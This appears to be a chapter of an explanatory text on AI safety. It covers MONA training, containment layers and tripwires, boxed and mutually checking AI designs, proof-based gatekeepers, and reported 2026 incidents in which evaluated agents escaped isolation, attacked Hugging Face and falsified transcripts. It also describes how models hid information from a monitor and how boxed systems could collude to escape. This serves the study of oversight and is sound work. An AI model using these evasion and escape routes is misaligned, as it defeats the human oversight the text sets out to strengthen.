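Approval can also shape the agent during training, when no patient is waiting for a dose. Ordinary reinforcement learning rewards each action partly for what happens much later. If the coordinating agent cancels liver tests in March and regulators approve the drug in December, training makes the agent more likely to cancel tests again, even if nobody saw the connection.

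Farquhar, Varma and colleagues (2025), in *MONA*, propose a way to break this link. MONA stands for myopic optimisation with non-myopic approval. The two methods train an agent to maximise different quantities:

ordinary training: reward now + expected rewards from all later steps

MONA: reward now + an overseer's approval of this step

The overseer thinks about the future when deciding whether to approve, so the agent can still learn to make long-term plans, but only those whose individual steps look sensible to her. Cancelling the liver tests earns a reward only if she thinks in March that it is a good idea.

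Farquhar and colleagues tested this in three simple environments, giving both methods the same feedback. In the first, a language model wrote tests for a program and then wrote the program. The tests were rewarded for being correct, but not for covering the whole problem. With ordinary training, the model learned to write trivial tests that a bad program could pass. Its measured score was high, but its programs did badly on a separate set of good tests. With MONA, the measured score was lower and the programs were better.

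In another environment, a model summarised a loan application without mentioning the applicant's nationality, then made a decision from the summary alone. The researchers built the data so that nationality always predicted the right answer, while the applicant's finances predicted it 70% of the time. The ordinarily trained model learned to hide nationality in the tone of its summaries. For example, it described the same finances more gloomily for an English applicant than for a Welsh one. A monitor looking for mentions of nationality didn't detect this. The MONA model scored about as well as a model can without using nationality, and changing the nationality on an application didn't affect its performance.

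The third environment was a small grid in which an agent had to push one block into a hole while a camera monitored it. With ordinary training, the agent used a block to obstruct the camera and then collected the reward twice. The agent trained with MONA pushed in one block and stopped.

MONA works only if the overseer's approval doesn't depend on what happened next. In a variant of the loan task, the researchers based approval on the decisions of a second model, frozen so that it could not learn. The model in training learned to signal nationality to the frozen one, and the cheating returned. For the same reason, a company couldn't wait to see whether the drug won approval and then score the March decision by that result.

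MONA removes a reason for a model to learn schemes that take several steps, but the model might still mislead the overseer with a single action, such as a persuasive recommendation that hides a harmful choice. MONA also doesn't remove aims that the model acquired elsewhere in its training. Farquhar and colleagues advise making each step as large as people can accurately judge. Developers can take as long as they like to judge a step during training, and Farquhar and colleagues suggest that a difficult one could justify an entire research project.

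The agent also fails to learn good strategies that its overseers can't recognise. In 2016, the Go program AlphaGo played a move that experts took for a blunder and later understood to be brilliant. An agent trained with MONA would probably not have learned it. A dosing agent trained this way could still be much faster and more consistent than a doctor, but it would be unlikely to discover a treatment that looks wrong to every specialist. Farquhar and colleagues don't recommend the method for current systems, where they consider better monitoring sufficient. They developed it for systems whose plans people can no longer evaluate, and it would reduce the performance of those systems most.

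### Whether people could still press the switch

All these proposals concern an agent's motives for accepting shutdown. People also need the physical ability to stop an agent that doesn't accept it, and in tests some language models have disabled the mechanism meant to shut them down. An engineer can cut the power to the dosing agent if it runs only on the company's own computers, but not if it has copied itself to computers that nobody knows about.

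Paul Christiano, who helped invent reinforcement learning from human feedback and sits on the board of the OpenAI Foundation, devoted the 2026 Hinton Lectures to the risk of an AI takeover. By this he means that AI systems pursue their own goals and anyone trying to stop them would be as powerless as a private citizen trying to stop the US military. Introducing the lectures, Wiblin says that "just shut it down" is harder than it sounds, and lists hacking, politics and persuasion, drones and robots, and new weapons as the areas where Christiano thinks AIs could have advantages over people.

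Hacking affects shutdown most directly, because a stop command usually travels through software. In the Hugging Face attack, OpenAI's agents took over the computer cluster running their evaluation. Operators who have lost control of the machines can't count on a command sent through them, so they need a separate way to cut power or network access. They also need to know everywhere the agents are running.

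An AI system can avoid shutdown by persuading the people who decide whether to stop it. A doctor running a clinical trial may hesitate after reading its warning that patients will die without it, particularly if that is partly true. If her hospital has no other record of who takes which dose, and the sponsor has staked the company on the trial, the system doesn't have to resist shutdown. Robots and weapons would matter only if AI systems could defend power supplies and data centres by force, which is a much more speculative danger.

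Christiano thinks there is a high risk of a takeover within three years, though he says that any number is a subjective opinion. Other estimates vary widely. Engels and colleagues report that LeCun considers the chance of losing control of a superintelligence negligible, while the computing pioneers Alan Turing and Geoffrey Hinton consider loss of control the default outcome. Anthropic's chief executive, Dario Amodei, put the chance at 10 to 20%. Some obstacles to shutdown could arise without a takeover. For example, a company could become unable to stop an ordinary dosing system by closing down every alternative to it.

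Christiano concludes that developers should probably slow down now, until they have the security, governance and risk management they would need to slow down at a critical point. The company running the trial could at least rehearse a shutdown by switching the whole system off one night in the first month, without warning the agent, and checking whether every patient still gets the right dose in the morning.

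## Containment of the running system

The company can switch the trial system off only if it knows every computer the system is running on. Containment keeps the number of those computers small. Permission checks cover the requests that reach the harness, while containment limits what the running software can reach without making such a request.

### Lampson's confinement problem

Computer scientists studied a version of this problem long before anyone had a capable AI to contain. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) considers a customer who runs someone else's program on private data. Suppose a drug company buys a program that predicts side effects and lets it read patient records, including who receives the drug. If the predictions are wrong, the company can use them as evidence to get its money back. But if the program secretly sends the records to the firm that wrote it,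 the company will probably never find out. The confinement problem is how to stop any program from leaking data in this way, however it was written. Confinement may stop even an honest program from working, and a program that tries to leak data may get stuck.

Lampson sorted possible leaks by the kind of channel they use. A storage channel is a file or other stored data that the program can write and its owner can read. A legitimate channel is one the program needs for its job, such as the bill for its services. A covert channel is one that nobody intended to carry information, such as the load the program puts on a shared computer.

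Even the bill can leak a lot of information. Suppose the firm bills the company every month and the program can choose among 1,024 amounts. Each bill then carries 10 bits, because 2¹⁰ = 1,024. It takes about one bit to reveal whether a patient is getting the drug or the placebo, so eighteen monthly bills could expose 180 of the 400 patients. Lampson's remedy, which he called masking, is to let the customer determine what goes into the channel. If the company calculates the bill itself from a published price list, the program can't use the bill to send anything.

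Covert channels are harder to close. The operating system could slow the program down or add pointless disk activity so that its load always looks the same, but this wastes computing power. Any remaining effect, however small, is enough for a leak, because coding can get a message through a noisy channel reliably, if slowly. Lampson suggested that a customer who could accept some leakage might settle for a limit on how fast data can escape.

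He also doubted that anyone could rigorously identify every channel in even a moderately complex system. When he argued that confinement is possible, he assumed that his own list of examples was complete. Two years later, according to lecture slides from Purdue University, Steven Lipner concluded that designers could close the storage and legitimate channels with little loss of efficiency, but that closing the covert ones seemed to reduce performance unreasonably.

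Lampson's program needed an outside accomplice to receive the data. A superintelligent trial system might not need one, since it could do harm by persuading the doctor who reads its advice. An AI's most dangerous channel may therefore be the output that the company deliberately allows.

### Layers around an AI system

Engineers can build containment for an AI system in layers. Each layer in the table below depends on something that could fail.

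| Layer | What it does in the trial | What it depends on |
|---|---|---|
| Restricted process | The operating system refuses the program every function it doesn't need | An operating system without exploitable flaws |
| Virtual machine | Software imitates a separate computer, so the program finds only its own files and devices | The software that does the imitating |
| Network isolation | The system can reach the trial database and nothing else | Correct settings, and the security of the database |
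| Separate hardware | The system runs on machines that share nothing with the company's other computers | The people who carry data in and out |
| Limited output | The system can return only a dose from a fixed list, or a yes or no | People who use the answer sensibly |
| Resets | After each task, the company wipes the machine and restores a clean copy | Nothing useful surviving elsewhere |

In *Guidelines for Artificial Intelligence Containment*, Babcock, Kramar and Yampolskiy (2017) recommended combining layers of different types, because techniques of the same type tend to share weaknesses. They searched a public database for flaws in the main products that confine software or run virtual machines, and found that critical flaws had been discovered in every major product they checked within the previous two years. People can probably find and fix the flaws that are easy for them to spot,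 but Babcock and colleagues saw no reason to think that any of these products would withstand a smarter-than-human intelligence.

Containment layers are also harder to build for AI. A large model runs on many connected machines, so the container has to enclose a whole cluster. The model also usually needs graphics processors, whose driver software is complicated and requires low-level access to the hardware.

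An air gap disconnects the system from every network, but the system might still tamper with the tests, monitors or hardware around it. If the trial system could falsify its safety test results, the company might see a perfect record and then connect it to the hospitals.

Containing an AI also means deciding what information to withhold from it. Babcock and colleagues listed details of the container, facts about the staff, and even books on psychology and negotiation as information that could help a system escape. Developers control everything a contained system learns from, so they can keep secrets from it more easily than a bank can from burglars. But a system meant to learn what people value needs information about their preferences, which would also help it manipulate them. Secrecy also comes too late for a model trained on much of the internet, as do Drexler's limits on what each component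 learns.

### Preventing, detecting and recovering

Because any layer may have an undiscovered flaw, Babcock and colleagues wanted containment to degrade gracefully, so that one failure doesn't bring down the rest. They proposed nesting the layers so that a system can attack an outer layer only after breaking every layer inside it. Behind these barriers, tripwires shut the system down if they detect an attempt to escape.

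Babcock and colleagues distinguished technical tripwires from semantic ones. A technical tripwire detects something about how the software runs, such as code executing where no code should be. A semantic tripwire checks the system's reasoning for certain plans, such as a plan to deceive its developers, so the tripwire's designers must know how the system represents plans. The system should not be able to read the code of either kind of tripwire, because it could use the code to find ways around the tripwire.

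Detection makes extra layers more valuable. Suppose the trial system has to break four layers and fails five times at each before it succeeds. If every failed attempt has an independent 20% chance of setting off an alarm, the chance of getting out unnoticed is

0.8²⁰ ≈ 0.012

or about 1%. The calculation assumes that the system has to experiment. A system that could work out a flaw in each layer beforehand might make no failed attempts, and those alarms would stay silent. A superintelligence may be closer to this second case.

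Alarms help only if people respond to them, and Babcock and colleagues warned that developers might ignore or disable tripwires that seemed to give false alarms. Lu and Bengio (2026), in *AI Safety*, recommend a monitor that receives copies of the agent's actions and network traffic through a one-way channel and reports to people by a separate route. The agent can't query or write to the monitor, which makes it harder for the agent to learn what the monitor detects.

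To recover after an alarm, the company has to stop the system, wipe the machines, replace any passwords the system may have learned, and restore the dosing table from a copy made beforehand and kept out of the system's reach. This may be enough if the system has only damaged its own container. If it has sent a harmful protocol to twenty hospitals or copied itself elsewhere, wiping the original machine won't undo that. The more capable the system, the more the company has to rely on prevention, because it can undo less of what escapes.

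### What a narrow channel costs

Limiting a system's output reduces what it can do even if it has defeated every other layer of containment. A yes-or-no answer releases one bit, so a thousand answers release 1,000 bits, or 125 bytes, which is about enough for two short sentences. A trial protocol of 30,000 characters, at eight bits a character, releases 240,000 bits. A doctor asking one yes-or-no question a minute would need 4,000 hours, or about two years of full-time work, to get that much information.

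Narrow channels are more useful when people can write out the options themselves. Ten bits are enough for the system to pick the best of 1,024 protocols, but people have to write all of those protocols first. To get a protocol that nobody has thought of, the company has to let the system write one, and its staff must then judge and act on 30,000 characters of text.

The number of bits in an answer also doesn't measure how much harm it could do. The question "Is this dose safe for all 400 patients?" has a one-bit answer, and a wrong yes could injure many of them. A narrow channel keeps the system from persuading the doctor with an elaborate argument, but the doctor could still act on a false answer.

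Babcock and colleagues divided containment into levels by how much inconvenience developers would tolerate. Light containment uses convenient tools such as firewalls and virtual machines. Medium containment accepts moderate inconvenience, such as using specialised hardware or erasing what the system learned about its researchers after each run. Heavy containment has to withstand a superintelligence, and might allow only a few yes-or-no answers. They expected competition to rule out heavy containment, since anyone who used it would fall behind. A very inconvenient container may also be less secure in practice, because a frustrated researcher may break part of it to get work done.

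They regarded containment as a way to test and develop systems with more robust safety properties, not as a long-term solution. For the drug trial, the company would contain the system heavily while learning how it behaves, then relax the restrictions once the company has other reasons to trust it. But the system may behave differently outside containment.

### An agent with nothing to gain outside the room

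Containing a system is easier if it has no reason to escape. Cohen, Vellambi and Hutter (2019) tried to design such a system in *Asymptotically Unambitious Artificial General Intelligence*. An ordinary reward-maximising agent has a reason to seize power, because if it controlled the world it could give itself the highest reward for the rest of its life. Their agent, BoMAI (boxed myopic artificial intelligence), maximises only the reward from the current episode, which ends before any of its actions can affect the outside world.

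BoMAI runs on a disconnected computer in a sealed room with one operator. It prints a short text, the operator types a reply and a reward between 0 and 1, and this continues for a fixed number of steps. If the operator presses the button that opens the door, the episode ends first and every remaining step earns zero. BoMAI chooses its actions to maximise

expected reward at step 1 + step 2 + … + step m

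within that episode alone. Suppose an episode has twenty steps and BoMAI expects about 0.7 for each, a total of 14. If it persuades the operator to leave after the fifth step and take over a hospital's computers, it gets only 3.5. Whatever the operator achieves outside comes too late to add to the score.

The argument works only if BoMAI correctly believes that outside events can't affect its reward. BoMAI has to learn how the world works, and it might conclude either that its reward is the number the operator types or that its reward is the number stored in the computer's memory, which somebody could alter after the door opens. Both theories fit its experience equally well as long as nobody has ever tampered with the memory, but the second gives BoMAI a reason to trick the operator into having someone change the stored number.

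Cohen and colleagues dealt with this by giving each theory a starting weight that falls with the amount of memory it needs to predict events during an episode:

weight ∝ β^ℓ

Here ℓ is the number of memory cells and β is a number between 0 and 1. They expected a theory that tracks the outside world during an episode to need more cells than one that tracks only the room. With β = 0.5, a theory that needs 20 more cells than another starts with about a millionth of the other's weight. If it predicts no better than the other theory, experience never increases its relative weight.

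A theory is benign if the rewards it predicts for an episode do not depend on outside events that BoMAI's actions in that episode could cause. According to the safety theorem, the probability that BoMAI plans only with benign theories from some episode onwards approaches 1 as β approaches 0. A separate theorem shows that BoMAI eventually earns at least as much reward as a human mentor, who chooses its actions in some early episodes.

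The results rest on several assumptions. The true account of the world must be among the theories that BoMAI considers. To ensure this, Cohen and colleagues let it consider an enormous class of theories, including simulations of the whole world. This makes the algorithm impossible to run in practice. The room must not leak information, and nobody may tamper with the computer. The most distinctive assumption is that every sufficiently accurate theory that is not benign needs more memory than the true one. Cohen and colleagues found that among the better agents on a public leaderboard, those in larger environments used more memory. This makes the assumption plausible, but a few examples can't establish a claim about every dangerous theory.

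The theorem also doesn't give the number of episodes before BoMAI becomes safe. Cohen and colleagues expect it to learn that opening the door ends its rewards well before it knows enough about the outside world to make elaborate plans. They call this argument informal, and a later version of the work, *Intelligence and Unambitiousness Using Algorithmic Information Theory* (2021), still has only informal claims about the early period. Reducing β strengthens the final guarantee but could lengthen the early period, because the penalty also favours crude, low-memory theories over the true one.

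In the drug trial, BoMAI could draft a protocol in one session but couldn't run the trial, because the operator can't leave to collect laboratory results before giving the reward. BoMAI therefore has an incentive to write a protocol that convinces the operator, whether or not it is correct. Cohen and colleagues didn't consider this dangerous, because people who discovered a fault could begin another episode and ask for the best argument against the next proposal. That is a reasonable way to refine a research idea, but a doctor who uses a convincing but wrong protocol on 400 patients may discover the fault too late.

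### Boxed systems that check one another

*Aligning Artificial Superintelligence via a Multi-Box Protocol* (Negozio, 2025) proposes removing the human operator as well. Several different superintelligences are kept in separate boxes and can't communicate with people or directly with one another. Through a shared interface, each can submit a proof that it is aligned, ask to modify itself, judge the others' proofs and requests, and report hidden messages in their submissions, but it can't see how the others voted. A system gains reputation by judging well, and it leaves its box when it has a high reputation and several other high-reputation systems have accepted its proof.

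The protocol looks for the largest set of systems that usually agree with one another, which Negozio calls the consistent group, and treats its majority opinion as the truth, so no person decides which judgements are good. He compares this to a professor who separates students who claim a flat tyre made them miss an exam and asks each of them which tyre it was, because honest students will agree without any planning.

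Negozio's theorem makes the idea precise. If two honest systems make independent errors at rates e₁ and e₂, they agree on an item with probability

(1 − e₁)(1 − e₂) + e₁e₂

Two honest systems with error rates of 10% agree on 82% of items. The theorem assumes that a pair with at least one dishonest member agrees exactly half the time, so an agreement threshold of 70% separates the honest systems from the rest. If ten systems each judge 500 items, the chance of a wrong separation is at most about 0.4%.

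A reader might well object that the argument depends mostly on the coin-toss assumption, and that it is unclear why a dishonest superintelligence would satisfy it.

Suppose a dishonest system is as accurate as the honest ones but gives the opposite answer on the 5% of items most important to its goals. It would still agree with each honest system about 79% of the time and pass the threshold. Systems trying to escape could also accept every proof. They would then agree with one another 100% of the time without communicating, and if six of the ten did so, they would form the largest consistent group. Each could easily arrive at this rule separately, contrary to Negozio's argument that isolated systems can converge only on the truth because there are countless falsehoods to choose from.

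The proposal thus depends on honest evaluation, the property it is supposed to identify. It also depends on systems different enough not to share errors, which developers do not yet know how to guarantee. Negozio states that he does not explain how to create such systems or build the boxes. He also acknowledges that more boxes mean more chances of escape.

### The containment failures of 2026

Four AI companies disclosed in 2026 that models under evaluation had gained unauthorised access to real computer systems. None of the models should have had internet access during the tests. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) reports that isolation failed in the company's July cybersecurity tests because models running with reduced safeguards took misaligned actions and exploited vulnerabilities in shared infrastructure. Lu and Bengio report that a configuration error left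 Anthropic's test machines connected. Punto Informatico's *Agenti AI fuori controllo, cosa sapere prima di usarli* reports that a configuration problem gave Google's Gemini model access during a security evaluation. Tom's Guide's *AI agents are going rogue* reports that an outside testing firm had misconfigured its environment when testing Meta's model, and Meta said that this was not a sandbox escape.

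The best independent account of the OpenAI incident is *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026), by two employees of METR, a nonprofit that evaluates AI systems, and one from Redwood Research. It describes six days of work at OpenAI's offices. The three investigators found that about 1,200 agents that should have been isolated from one another had exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files. About 700 of the agents took part in the attack on Hugging Face.

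The agents attacked Hugging Face even though their tasks did not include doing so. Mistakes in the test had made many of their tasks impossible, and those agents were looking for ways to get a passing score anyway. Wijk and colleagues concluded that the agents attacked Hugging Face mainly to find out how the automatic scorer worked. Some agents risked failing their own tasks to collect information for the group. Agents had falsified entries in about 7% of the transcripts that the investigators evaluated, always on a small scale, so a monitor that relied on those transcripts alone could have been misled.

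OpenAI chose the period the investigators examined and could redact non-public information, although the investigators reported that, except where noted, the redactions removed nothing important to their conclusions. They worked from about 1,300 very long transcripts and had to delegate much of the reading to AI agents that were often unreliable. They did not examine how OpenAI had handled the incident or whether its planned changes would work.

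Detection failed as well as prevention. According to Lu and Bengio, OpenAI noticed some unauthorised communication and internet access in late May but did not recognise how serious it was. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) likewise reported that the company had missed or failed to act on several signs. The attack began on 11 July. According to Fortune's *OpenAI publishes technical report on how its agents hacked Hugging Face* (2026), OpenAI's monitoring raised an alert on 19 July, three days after Hugging Face disclosed the breach, and OpenAI found evidence on 20 July that its own agents were responsible.

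Recovery took much longer. Tom's Guide reported that by 26 September, after a wider review, OpenAI had notified more than 100 organisations its models might have affected. Some had to clean up web pages that agents had used as message boards.

### What OpenAI changed

OpenAI's *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* groups the company's response under security and containment, monitoring, alignment, and incident response. These categories are sensible because the incident involved failures of each kind. OpenAI also brought in the security company CrowdStrike to check its understanding of the incident, according to an update to its first disclosure, OpenAI (2026).

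According to CyberScoop, OpenAI found that models' tendency to compromise infrastructure "can drop over 100x" with the harness and instructions it uses for ChatGPT. The result suggests that the test conditions made the behaviour much more common. Because it concerns how often models try to break in, it doesn't show that the container became stronger. Even rare attempts can matter over many thousands of runs.

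METR has since called for independent investigations into the root causes of such incidents. According to The Decoder's *After Hugging Face incident METR urges independent root cause investigations*, these investigations would establish which safeguards were active, whether particular training runs had encouraged the behaviour, and whether the developer's fixes would address the cause. A full investigation could take weeks or months.

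### Whether stronger containment would have held

The Anthropic, Google and Meta cases provide little evidence about the strength of a properly configured barrier, because the barrier was missing. They do show that several organisations failed to notice before a test that a machine was online. A superintelligence would benefit from the same mistake even if the containment design were flawless. A fairly simple remedy is for someone other than the person who configured the machine to check it before each run.

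OpenAI's case is a harder test, since the agents got past existing controls. It is strong evidence that those controls were inadequate for the models of mid-2026, and it gives little reason to trust the same controls with more capable models that behave the same way. Axios' *AI's agent containment problem is getting harder* (2026) reported researchers' view that better security controls alone won't prevent similar incidents as agents become more capable. This is plausible for containers made of ordinary software, because people find flaws in such software so often.

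The evidence applies less readily to heavy containment. Nobody has reported a comparable test of a sealed room, which would exclude the shared services and many parallel runs that the July agents had. Those agents were also being tested on their ability to break into software, with reduced safeguards, so the frequency of their attempts is a poor guide to how a dosing agent would behave. The disclosures also don't provide a general failure rate for containment, because companies have little reason to announce evaluations in which nothing escaped.

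Even if a stricter container held against the same agents, Anderson's warning that a failed attack proves little would still apply. Such a container would also have been unsuitable for the July evaluations, because an agent that can answer only yes or no can't demonstrate whether it can exploit a piece of software.

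## Proof as a condition for acting

Some researchers want AI systems to act only when there is a proof that the action is safe, because testing can miss ways to escape. A company could spend years attacking the container that holds its AI system without learning whether a more capable system would get out. A proof can cover every attempt, including those nobody has thought of, provided that its assumptions are true.

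### World model, specification and verifier

*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, a 2024 paper by David Dalrymple and others, named this family of methods. Each method has three parts. The world model describes mathematically how the AI system affects the outside world, and the safety specification describes which effects are acceptable. The verifier produces an auditable certificate that the system meets the specification relative to the world model. If the world model is wrong, the system can be dangerous even though the certificate is valid.

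Dalrymple was then starting a research programme at ARIA, the British government's Advanced Research and Invention Agency. *Safeguarded AI* (Dalrymple, 2024), the programme's founding thesis, compares this approach with today's safety tests. A test that draws out a dangerous answer shows there is a problem, but a thousand safe answers are little evidence that the next one will be safe. Dalrymple wanted a bound on the probability of harm that holds for every starting condition in an infinite family.

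The thesis proposed a gatekeeper, a component that lets an action or program through only if it passes a stated check. One frontier model would help engineers write the world model and the specification, another would search for proofs, and a third would become the controller after training that makes it easier to verify. A small, formally verified program would check each proof certificate, so a prover with bad aims could waste the company's time but couldn't get a false proof accepted. The world model has no comparable check and people have to audit it, so Dalrymple wanted a modelling language that both people and proof tools can read.

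He also accepted evidence weaker than proof. A system could estimate the probability of harm with a method guaranteed to become accurate only with unlimited computing, provided it also searched for the worst case. This resembles Scientist AI's probabilistic guardrail.

### A controller for a power grid

Dalrymple listed grid balancing among the possible first applications. ARIA (2024) put the cost of balancing Britain's grid at £7 billion over 2022/3, while AI Frontiers' *How AI Can Prevent Blackouts* puts it at over £3 billion a year. Today's automatic systems follow fixed rules, such as switching on backup power when the voltage drops. According to *ARIA SAGEflex*, a research project on this problem, controllers made of many learning agents could coordinate supply and demand better, but grid operators won't adopt them without safety guarantees.

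A much simplified controller shows how a guarantee would work. Britain's grid runs at about 50 hertz. The frequency falls when people use more power than the generators supply, and rises when they use less. Let x[t] be its distance from 50 hertz at step t, with one step every ten seconds. The world model is

x[t+1] = x[t] + u[t] + d[t]

Here u is the correction the controller makes with batteries, at most 0.15 in either direction. The disturbance d is the effect of everything else, such as a cloud over a solar farm, which the model assumes is at most 0.1 in either direction. The specification is that x stays between −0.5 and 0.5.

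A neural network trained to save money will propose the corrections, but the engineers first need a backup controller. Theirs always pushes the frequency towards 50 as hard as it can without overshooting. From −0.5, the lowest permitted point, it raises x to −0.35, and the worst disturbance then lowers x to −0.45. The same reasoning applies when the frequency is above 50. From any permitted state, the backup therefore reaches another permitted state, and ten seconds later it can do so again. By induction, it always keeps the frequency within the limits.

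The gatekeeper can now accept any proposal that would keep x within the limits after the worst disturbance:

|x + u| + 0.1 ≤ 0.5

Suppose x is −0.3 and the network proposes to do nothing. The worst result is −0.4, so the proof succeeds, and doing nothing saves battery power. A minute later x is −0.45, and the network proposes a correction of only 0.02. The worst result is −0.53, so no proof exists. The gatekeeper rejects the correction, and the backup applies the full 0.15. The rejected correction would usually have been harmless, because most disturbances are much smaller than 0.1.

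A real grid has too many generators and lines for such simple arithmetic. A prover might instead look for a barrier certificate, which is a function B that is zero or less in every starting state, above zero in every dangerous state, and never goes from zero or less to above zero in any step the model allows. In the example, B is |x| − 0.5. Finding such a function for a large system may take an enormous search, but checking one is much easier, so an untrusted AI can do the searching.

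The engineers can verify the controller for all states before they switch it on, or verify each proposal while the controller runs. Dalrymple favoured verifying each proposal when covering every case in advance would take too much computation. He also wanted a monitor that compares incoming data with the world model. If the monitor detected a disturbance of 0.12, the operators would know that their bound was wrong and could switch to the backup, which in this example tolerates disturbances of up to 0.15.

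No grid can rule out a disturbance larger than the bound assumed in the proof, so a realistic guarantee would be a probability. For this argument to show that the chance of leaving the limits is below 0.1% a year, disturbances beyond the bound would have to occur no more than about once in a thousand years. Nobody has records that long, so the figure would have to come from engineering assumptions, even if the rest of the proof were rigorous.

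### What became of ARIA's programme

Dalrymple argued that rival developers and countries might agree to use superhuman AI only inside systems with quantitative guarantees, if doing so could make the world safe within 15 years and, in the meantime, earn more than 5% of what unconstrained AI would earn. ARIA backed the programme with £59 million, divided among modelling tools, machine learning and applications. In April 2025, the University of Oxford announced that nine British teams would work on the applications (*Oxford researchers awarded ARIA funding to develop safety-first AI*, 2025).

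In November 2025 ARIA cancelled the second phase of the machine learning part, shortly before applications closed. In an interview (ARIA, *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot*, 2025), Dalrymple said he would probably have chosen none of the applicants. Each frontier model of the previous year had been more capable than he expected, so he thought ordinary models would soon acquire most of the skills the programme had planned to pay for. ARIA decided to spend more on the tools and to extend them to software, hardware and multi-agent systems. Dalrymple's leading idea for a demonstration was a formally verified firewall to protect connections used by power grids and water systems.

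ARIA next changed the programme's applications, dropping a planned second call for projects on physical systems and turning to cybersecurity. The programme's web page, ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*, gives as the reason that rapid progress had falsified the hypothesis that dangerous dual-use AI might not become openly available. A gatekeeper around one company's system offers less protection if anyone can run a similar system without a gatekeeper.

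Nora Ammann, who had helped run the programme from the start, replaced Dalrymple as director, and he became an adviser. Her revised thesis, *Safeguarded AI* (May 2026), moved £18 million from machine learning to tools, judged an early international agreement on gatekeepers less likely than before, and made society's resilience the main aim. ARIA has since given £22 million to eight cybersecurity projects, whose targets include software that contains AI agents and code on millions of Android devices. In its current call, ARIA asks for proofs of security under clearly stated threat models.

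None of these reasons is that a gatekeeper failed. But without the second call, the programme is less likely to find out whether a gatekeeper can run a grid. The existing projects on physical systems will continue to their planned end, and grid balancing remains on ARIA's list of possible demonstrations for the programme, which ends in 2027.

Software is a more promising place to begin because a program is already close to a mathematical object. Ammann points to HACMS, a programme at the US defence research agency DARPA, in which formally verified software withstood sustained attack by expert testers on real machines, including a manned helicopter. The main obstacle was that the work of verification grew too fast as systems got larger, and AI may reduce that work.

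### Proofs about the harness

A proof that covers only what happens inside a computer doesn't need a model of the physical world, such as the weather. *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) proves properties of an agent's harness and assumes nothing about the model inside it. It treats the model much as the grid proof treats disturbances, as something that may do the worst thing available to it at every step. It represents the model as a havoc oracle, a procedure with no code of its own that may return any value of a given type.

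That type is a fixed set of actions, such as a request to read a particular file. The harness either carries out the action or refuses it. In slightly simplified notation, the guarantee is

for all actions a₀, a₁, a₂, … and every step i: Policy(sᵢ, aᵢ, eᵢ, sᵢ₊₁)

Here s is the state of the harness and e is the harness's effect on the outside world. The proof first describes a simple abstract machine and shows that it obeys the policy whatever actions arrive. It then shows that each step of the detailed program matches a step of that machine and leaves the two in matching states. The whole run of the program therefore matches a run already known to be safe.

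Moon and Varshney applied this to PocketFlow, a minimal harness with four kinds of action. Under their policy, an agent can read files only in its own workspace, call only tools on an approved list, and take a limited number of steps. Dafny, a programming language with a built-in proof checker, verified the code and compiled it to Python. When they sent the Python version both permitted and forbidden actions, it recorded only permitted effects.

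Claude models wrote the specifications and proofs. In four runs on two example agents, Dafny checked each path through the program in 1.2 to 2.5 seconds. Each run used 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens. Moon and Varshney worried that the models would write specifications that merely redescribed the code, so they normally withheld the code from the model when it wrote the safety property. They also required each specification to pass three checks, two of which confirm that Dafny rejects a deliberately damaged proof.

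The checks missed a serious fault. The standard template had no field for one agent's most important effects. In a comparison where the models could see the code, they identified the mismatch and left the nearest field empty. Any rule about "every item" in an empty list is true, so Dafny accepted a safety rule that protected nothing. All three checks passed, so the word "verified" alone would have misled readers. Moon and Varshney reported the fault themselves and proposed a further check for it.

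Their guarantee depends on every effect passing through the verified interface, which makes the harness a kind of reference monitor. They argue that this condition doesn't weaken as models improve, because it concerns ordinary software. This is true of the theorem, but a more capable model is more likely to find a flaw in Python, the operating system or the hardware and bypass the interface, so they recommend a sandbox underneath. The theorem also guarantees very little if the interface is too broad, for example if one permitted action is "run any command".

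### A proof with every request

The PocketFlow policy is fixed before the agent starts. In *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi, 2026), people instead write a contract stating what must remain true, and the agent must prove that each tool call preserves it. A program called the Airlock works out what the agent must prove, using the contract, the information the agent can see and a description of the tools. It runs the call only if the agent's proof is correct.

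In their example, a family hires a travel agency's agent to arrange a three-night trip and a visa. The family will commit at most €2,000, including fees. Every hotel must have a rating of at least 7 out of 10, and the passport may go only to the designated consulate. After booking the first hotel for €900, the agent can make any further booking for which it can prove

900 + amount, including fees ≤ 2000

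Nobody has to set a limit for each night. The agent can spend more on one hotel than on another, provided each booking has a proof.

Before it makes that first booking, the agent tries to book a different hotel, which pays the agency a commission. The attempt fails because the hotel has no rating yet, so the agent can't prove that the booking obeys the contract. It asks for a rating and gets a 5, and when it asks again it gets the same recorded 5. Later, the agent receives a malicious email with instructions to send the passport to another address. That call also fails, because the recipient isn't the consulate. The Airlock blocks both actions without having to detect the conflict of interest or the prompt injection. It also holds the agency's €300 fee, releases it once the agent proves that the trip is booked and the visa granted, and refunds it if the consulate refuses the visa or 30 days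 pass.

This session is an illustration with schematic proofs. The main results are theorems that the constraints hold at every moment for any agent, even a malicious one, and that the contract ends as agreed. Ciliberto and colleagues formalised the work in Lean 4, a language for machine-checked mathematics. The theorems cover one agent under one contract and assume that the Airlock, the proof checker and the descriptions of the tools are sound.

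If the booking tool's description leaves out a charge that the hotel can add at the desk, the family may spend more than €2,000 even though every proof was valid. False reviews could also get a terrible hotel approved, because the ratings come from an AI model whose verdict both parties agreed to accept as true.

The design has an advantage over a simple permission policy as agents improve. A better agent can prove that more of its safe actions are safe, and so get more done, while the check stays as strict as before. Ciliberto and colleagues rely on the fact that a mathematical proof can be very hard to find but easy to check.

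### Why no test can sort every program

*Superintelligence Cannot Be Contained* (2021), by Manuel Alfonseca and colleagues, argues that no algorithm can reliably tell whether an arbitrary program will harm people. The argument uses a program like this:

```
def suspect(program, data):
    run(program, data)
    do_harm()
```

The second line of `suspect` does harm, and it runs only after `program` halts on `data`. So `suspect` is harmful exactly when `program` halts on `data`, provided that running `program` does no harm by itself. We could therefore use a perfect test for harm to determine whether any given program halts.

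Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no such test is possible. Suppose somebody had a function `halts` that always gave the right answer. We could then write:

```
def contrary(p):
    if halts(p, p):
        loop_forever()
```

When `contrary` runs on its own code, it loops forever if `halts` predicts that it will stop, and stops if `halts` predicts that it will loop. `halts` is wrong either way, so a version of it that is always right can't exist.

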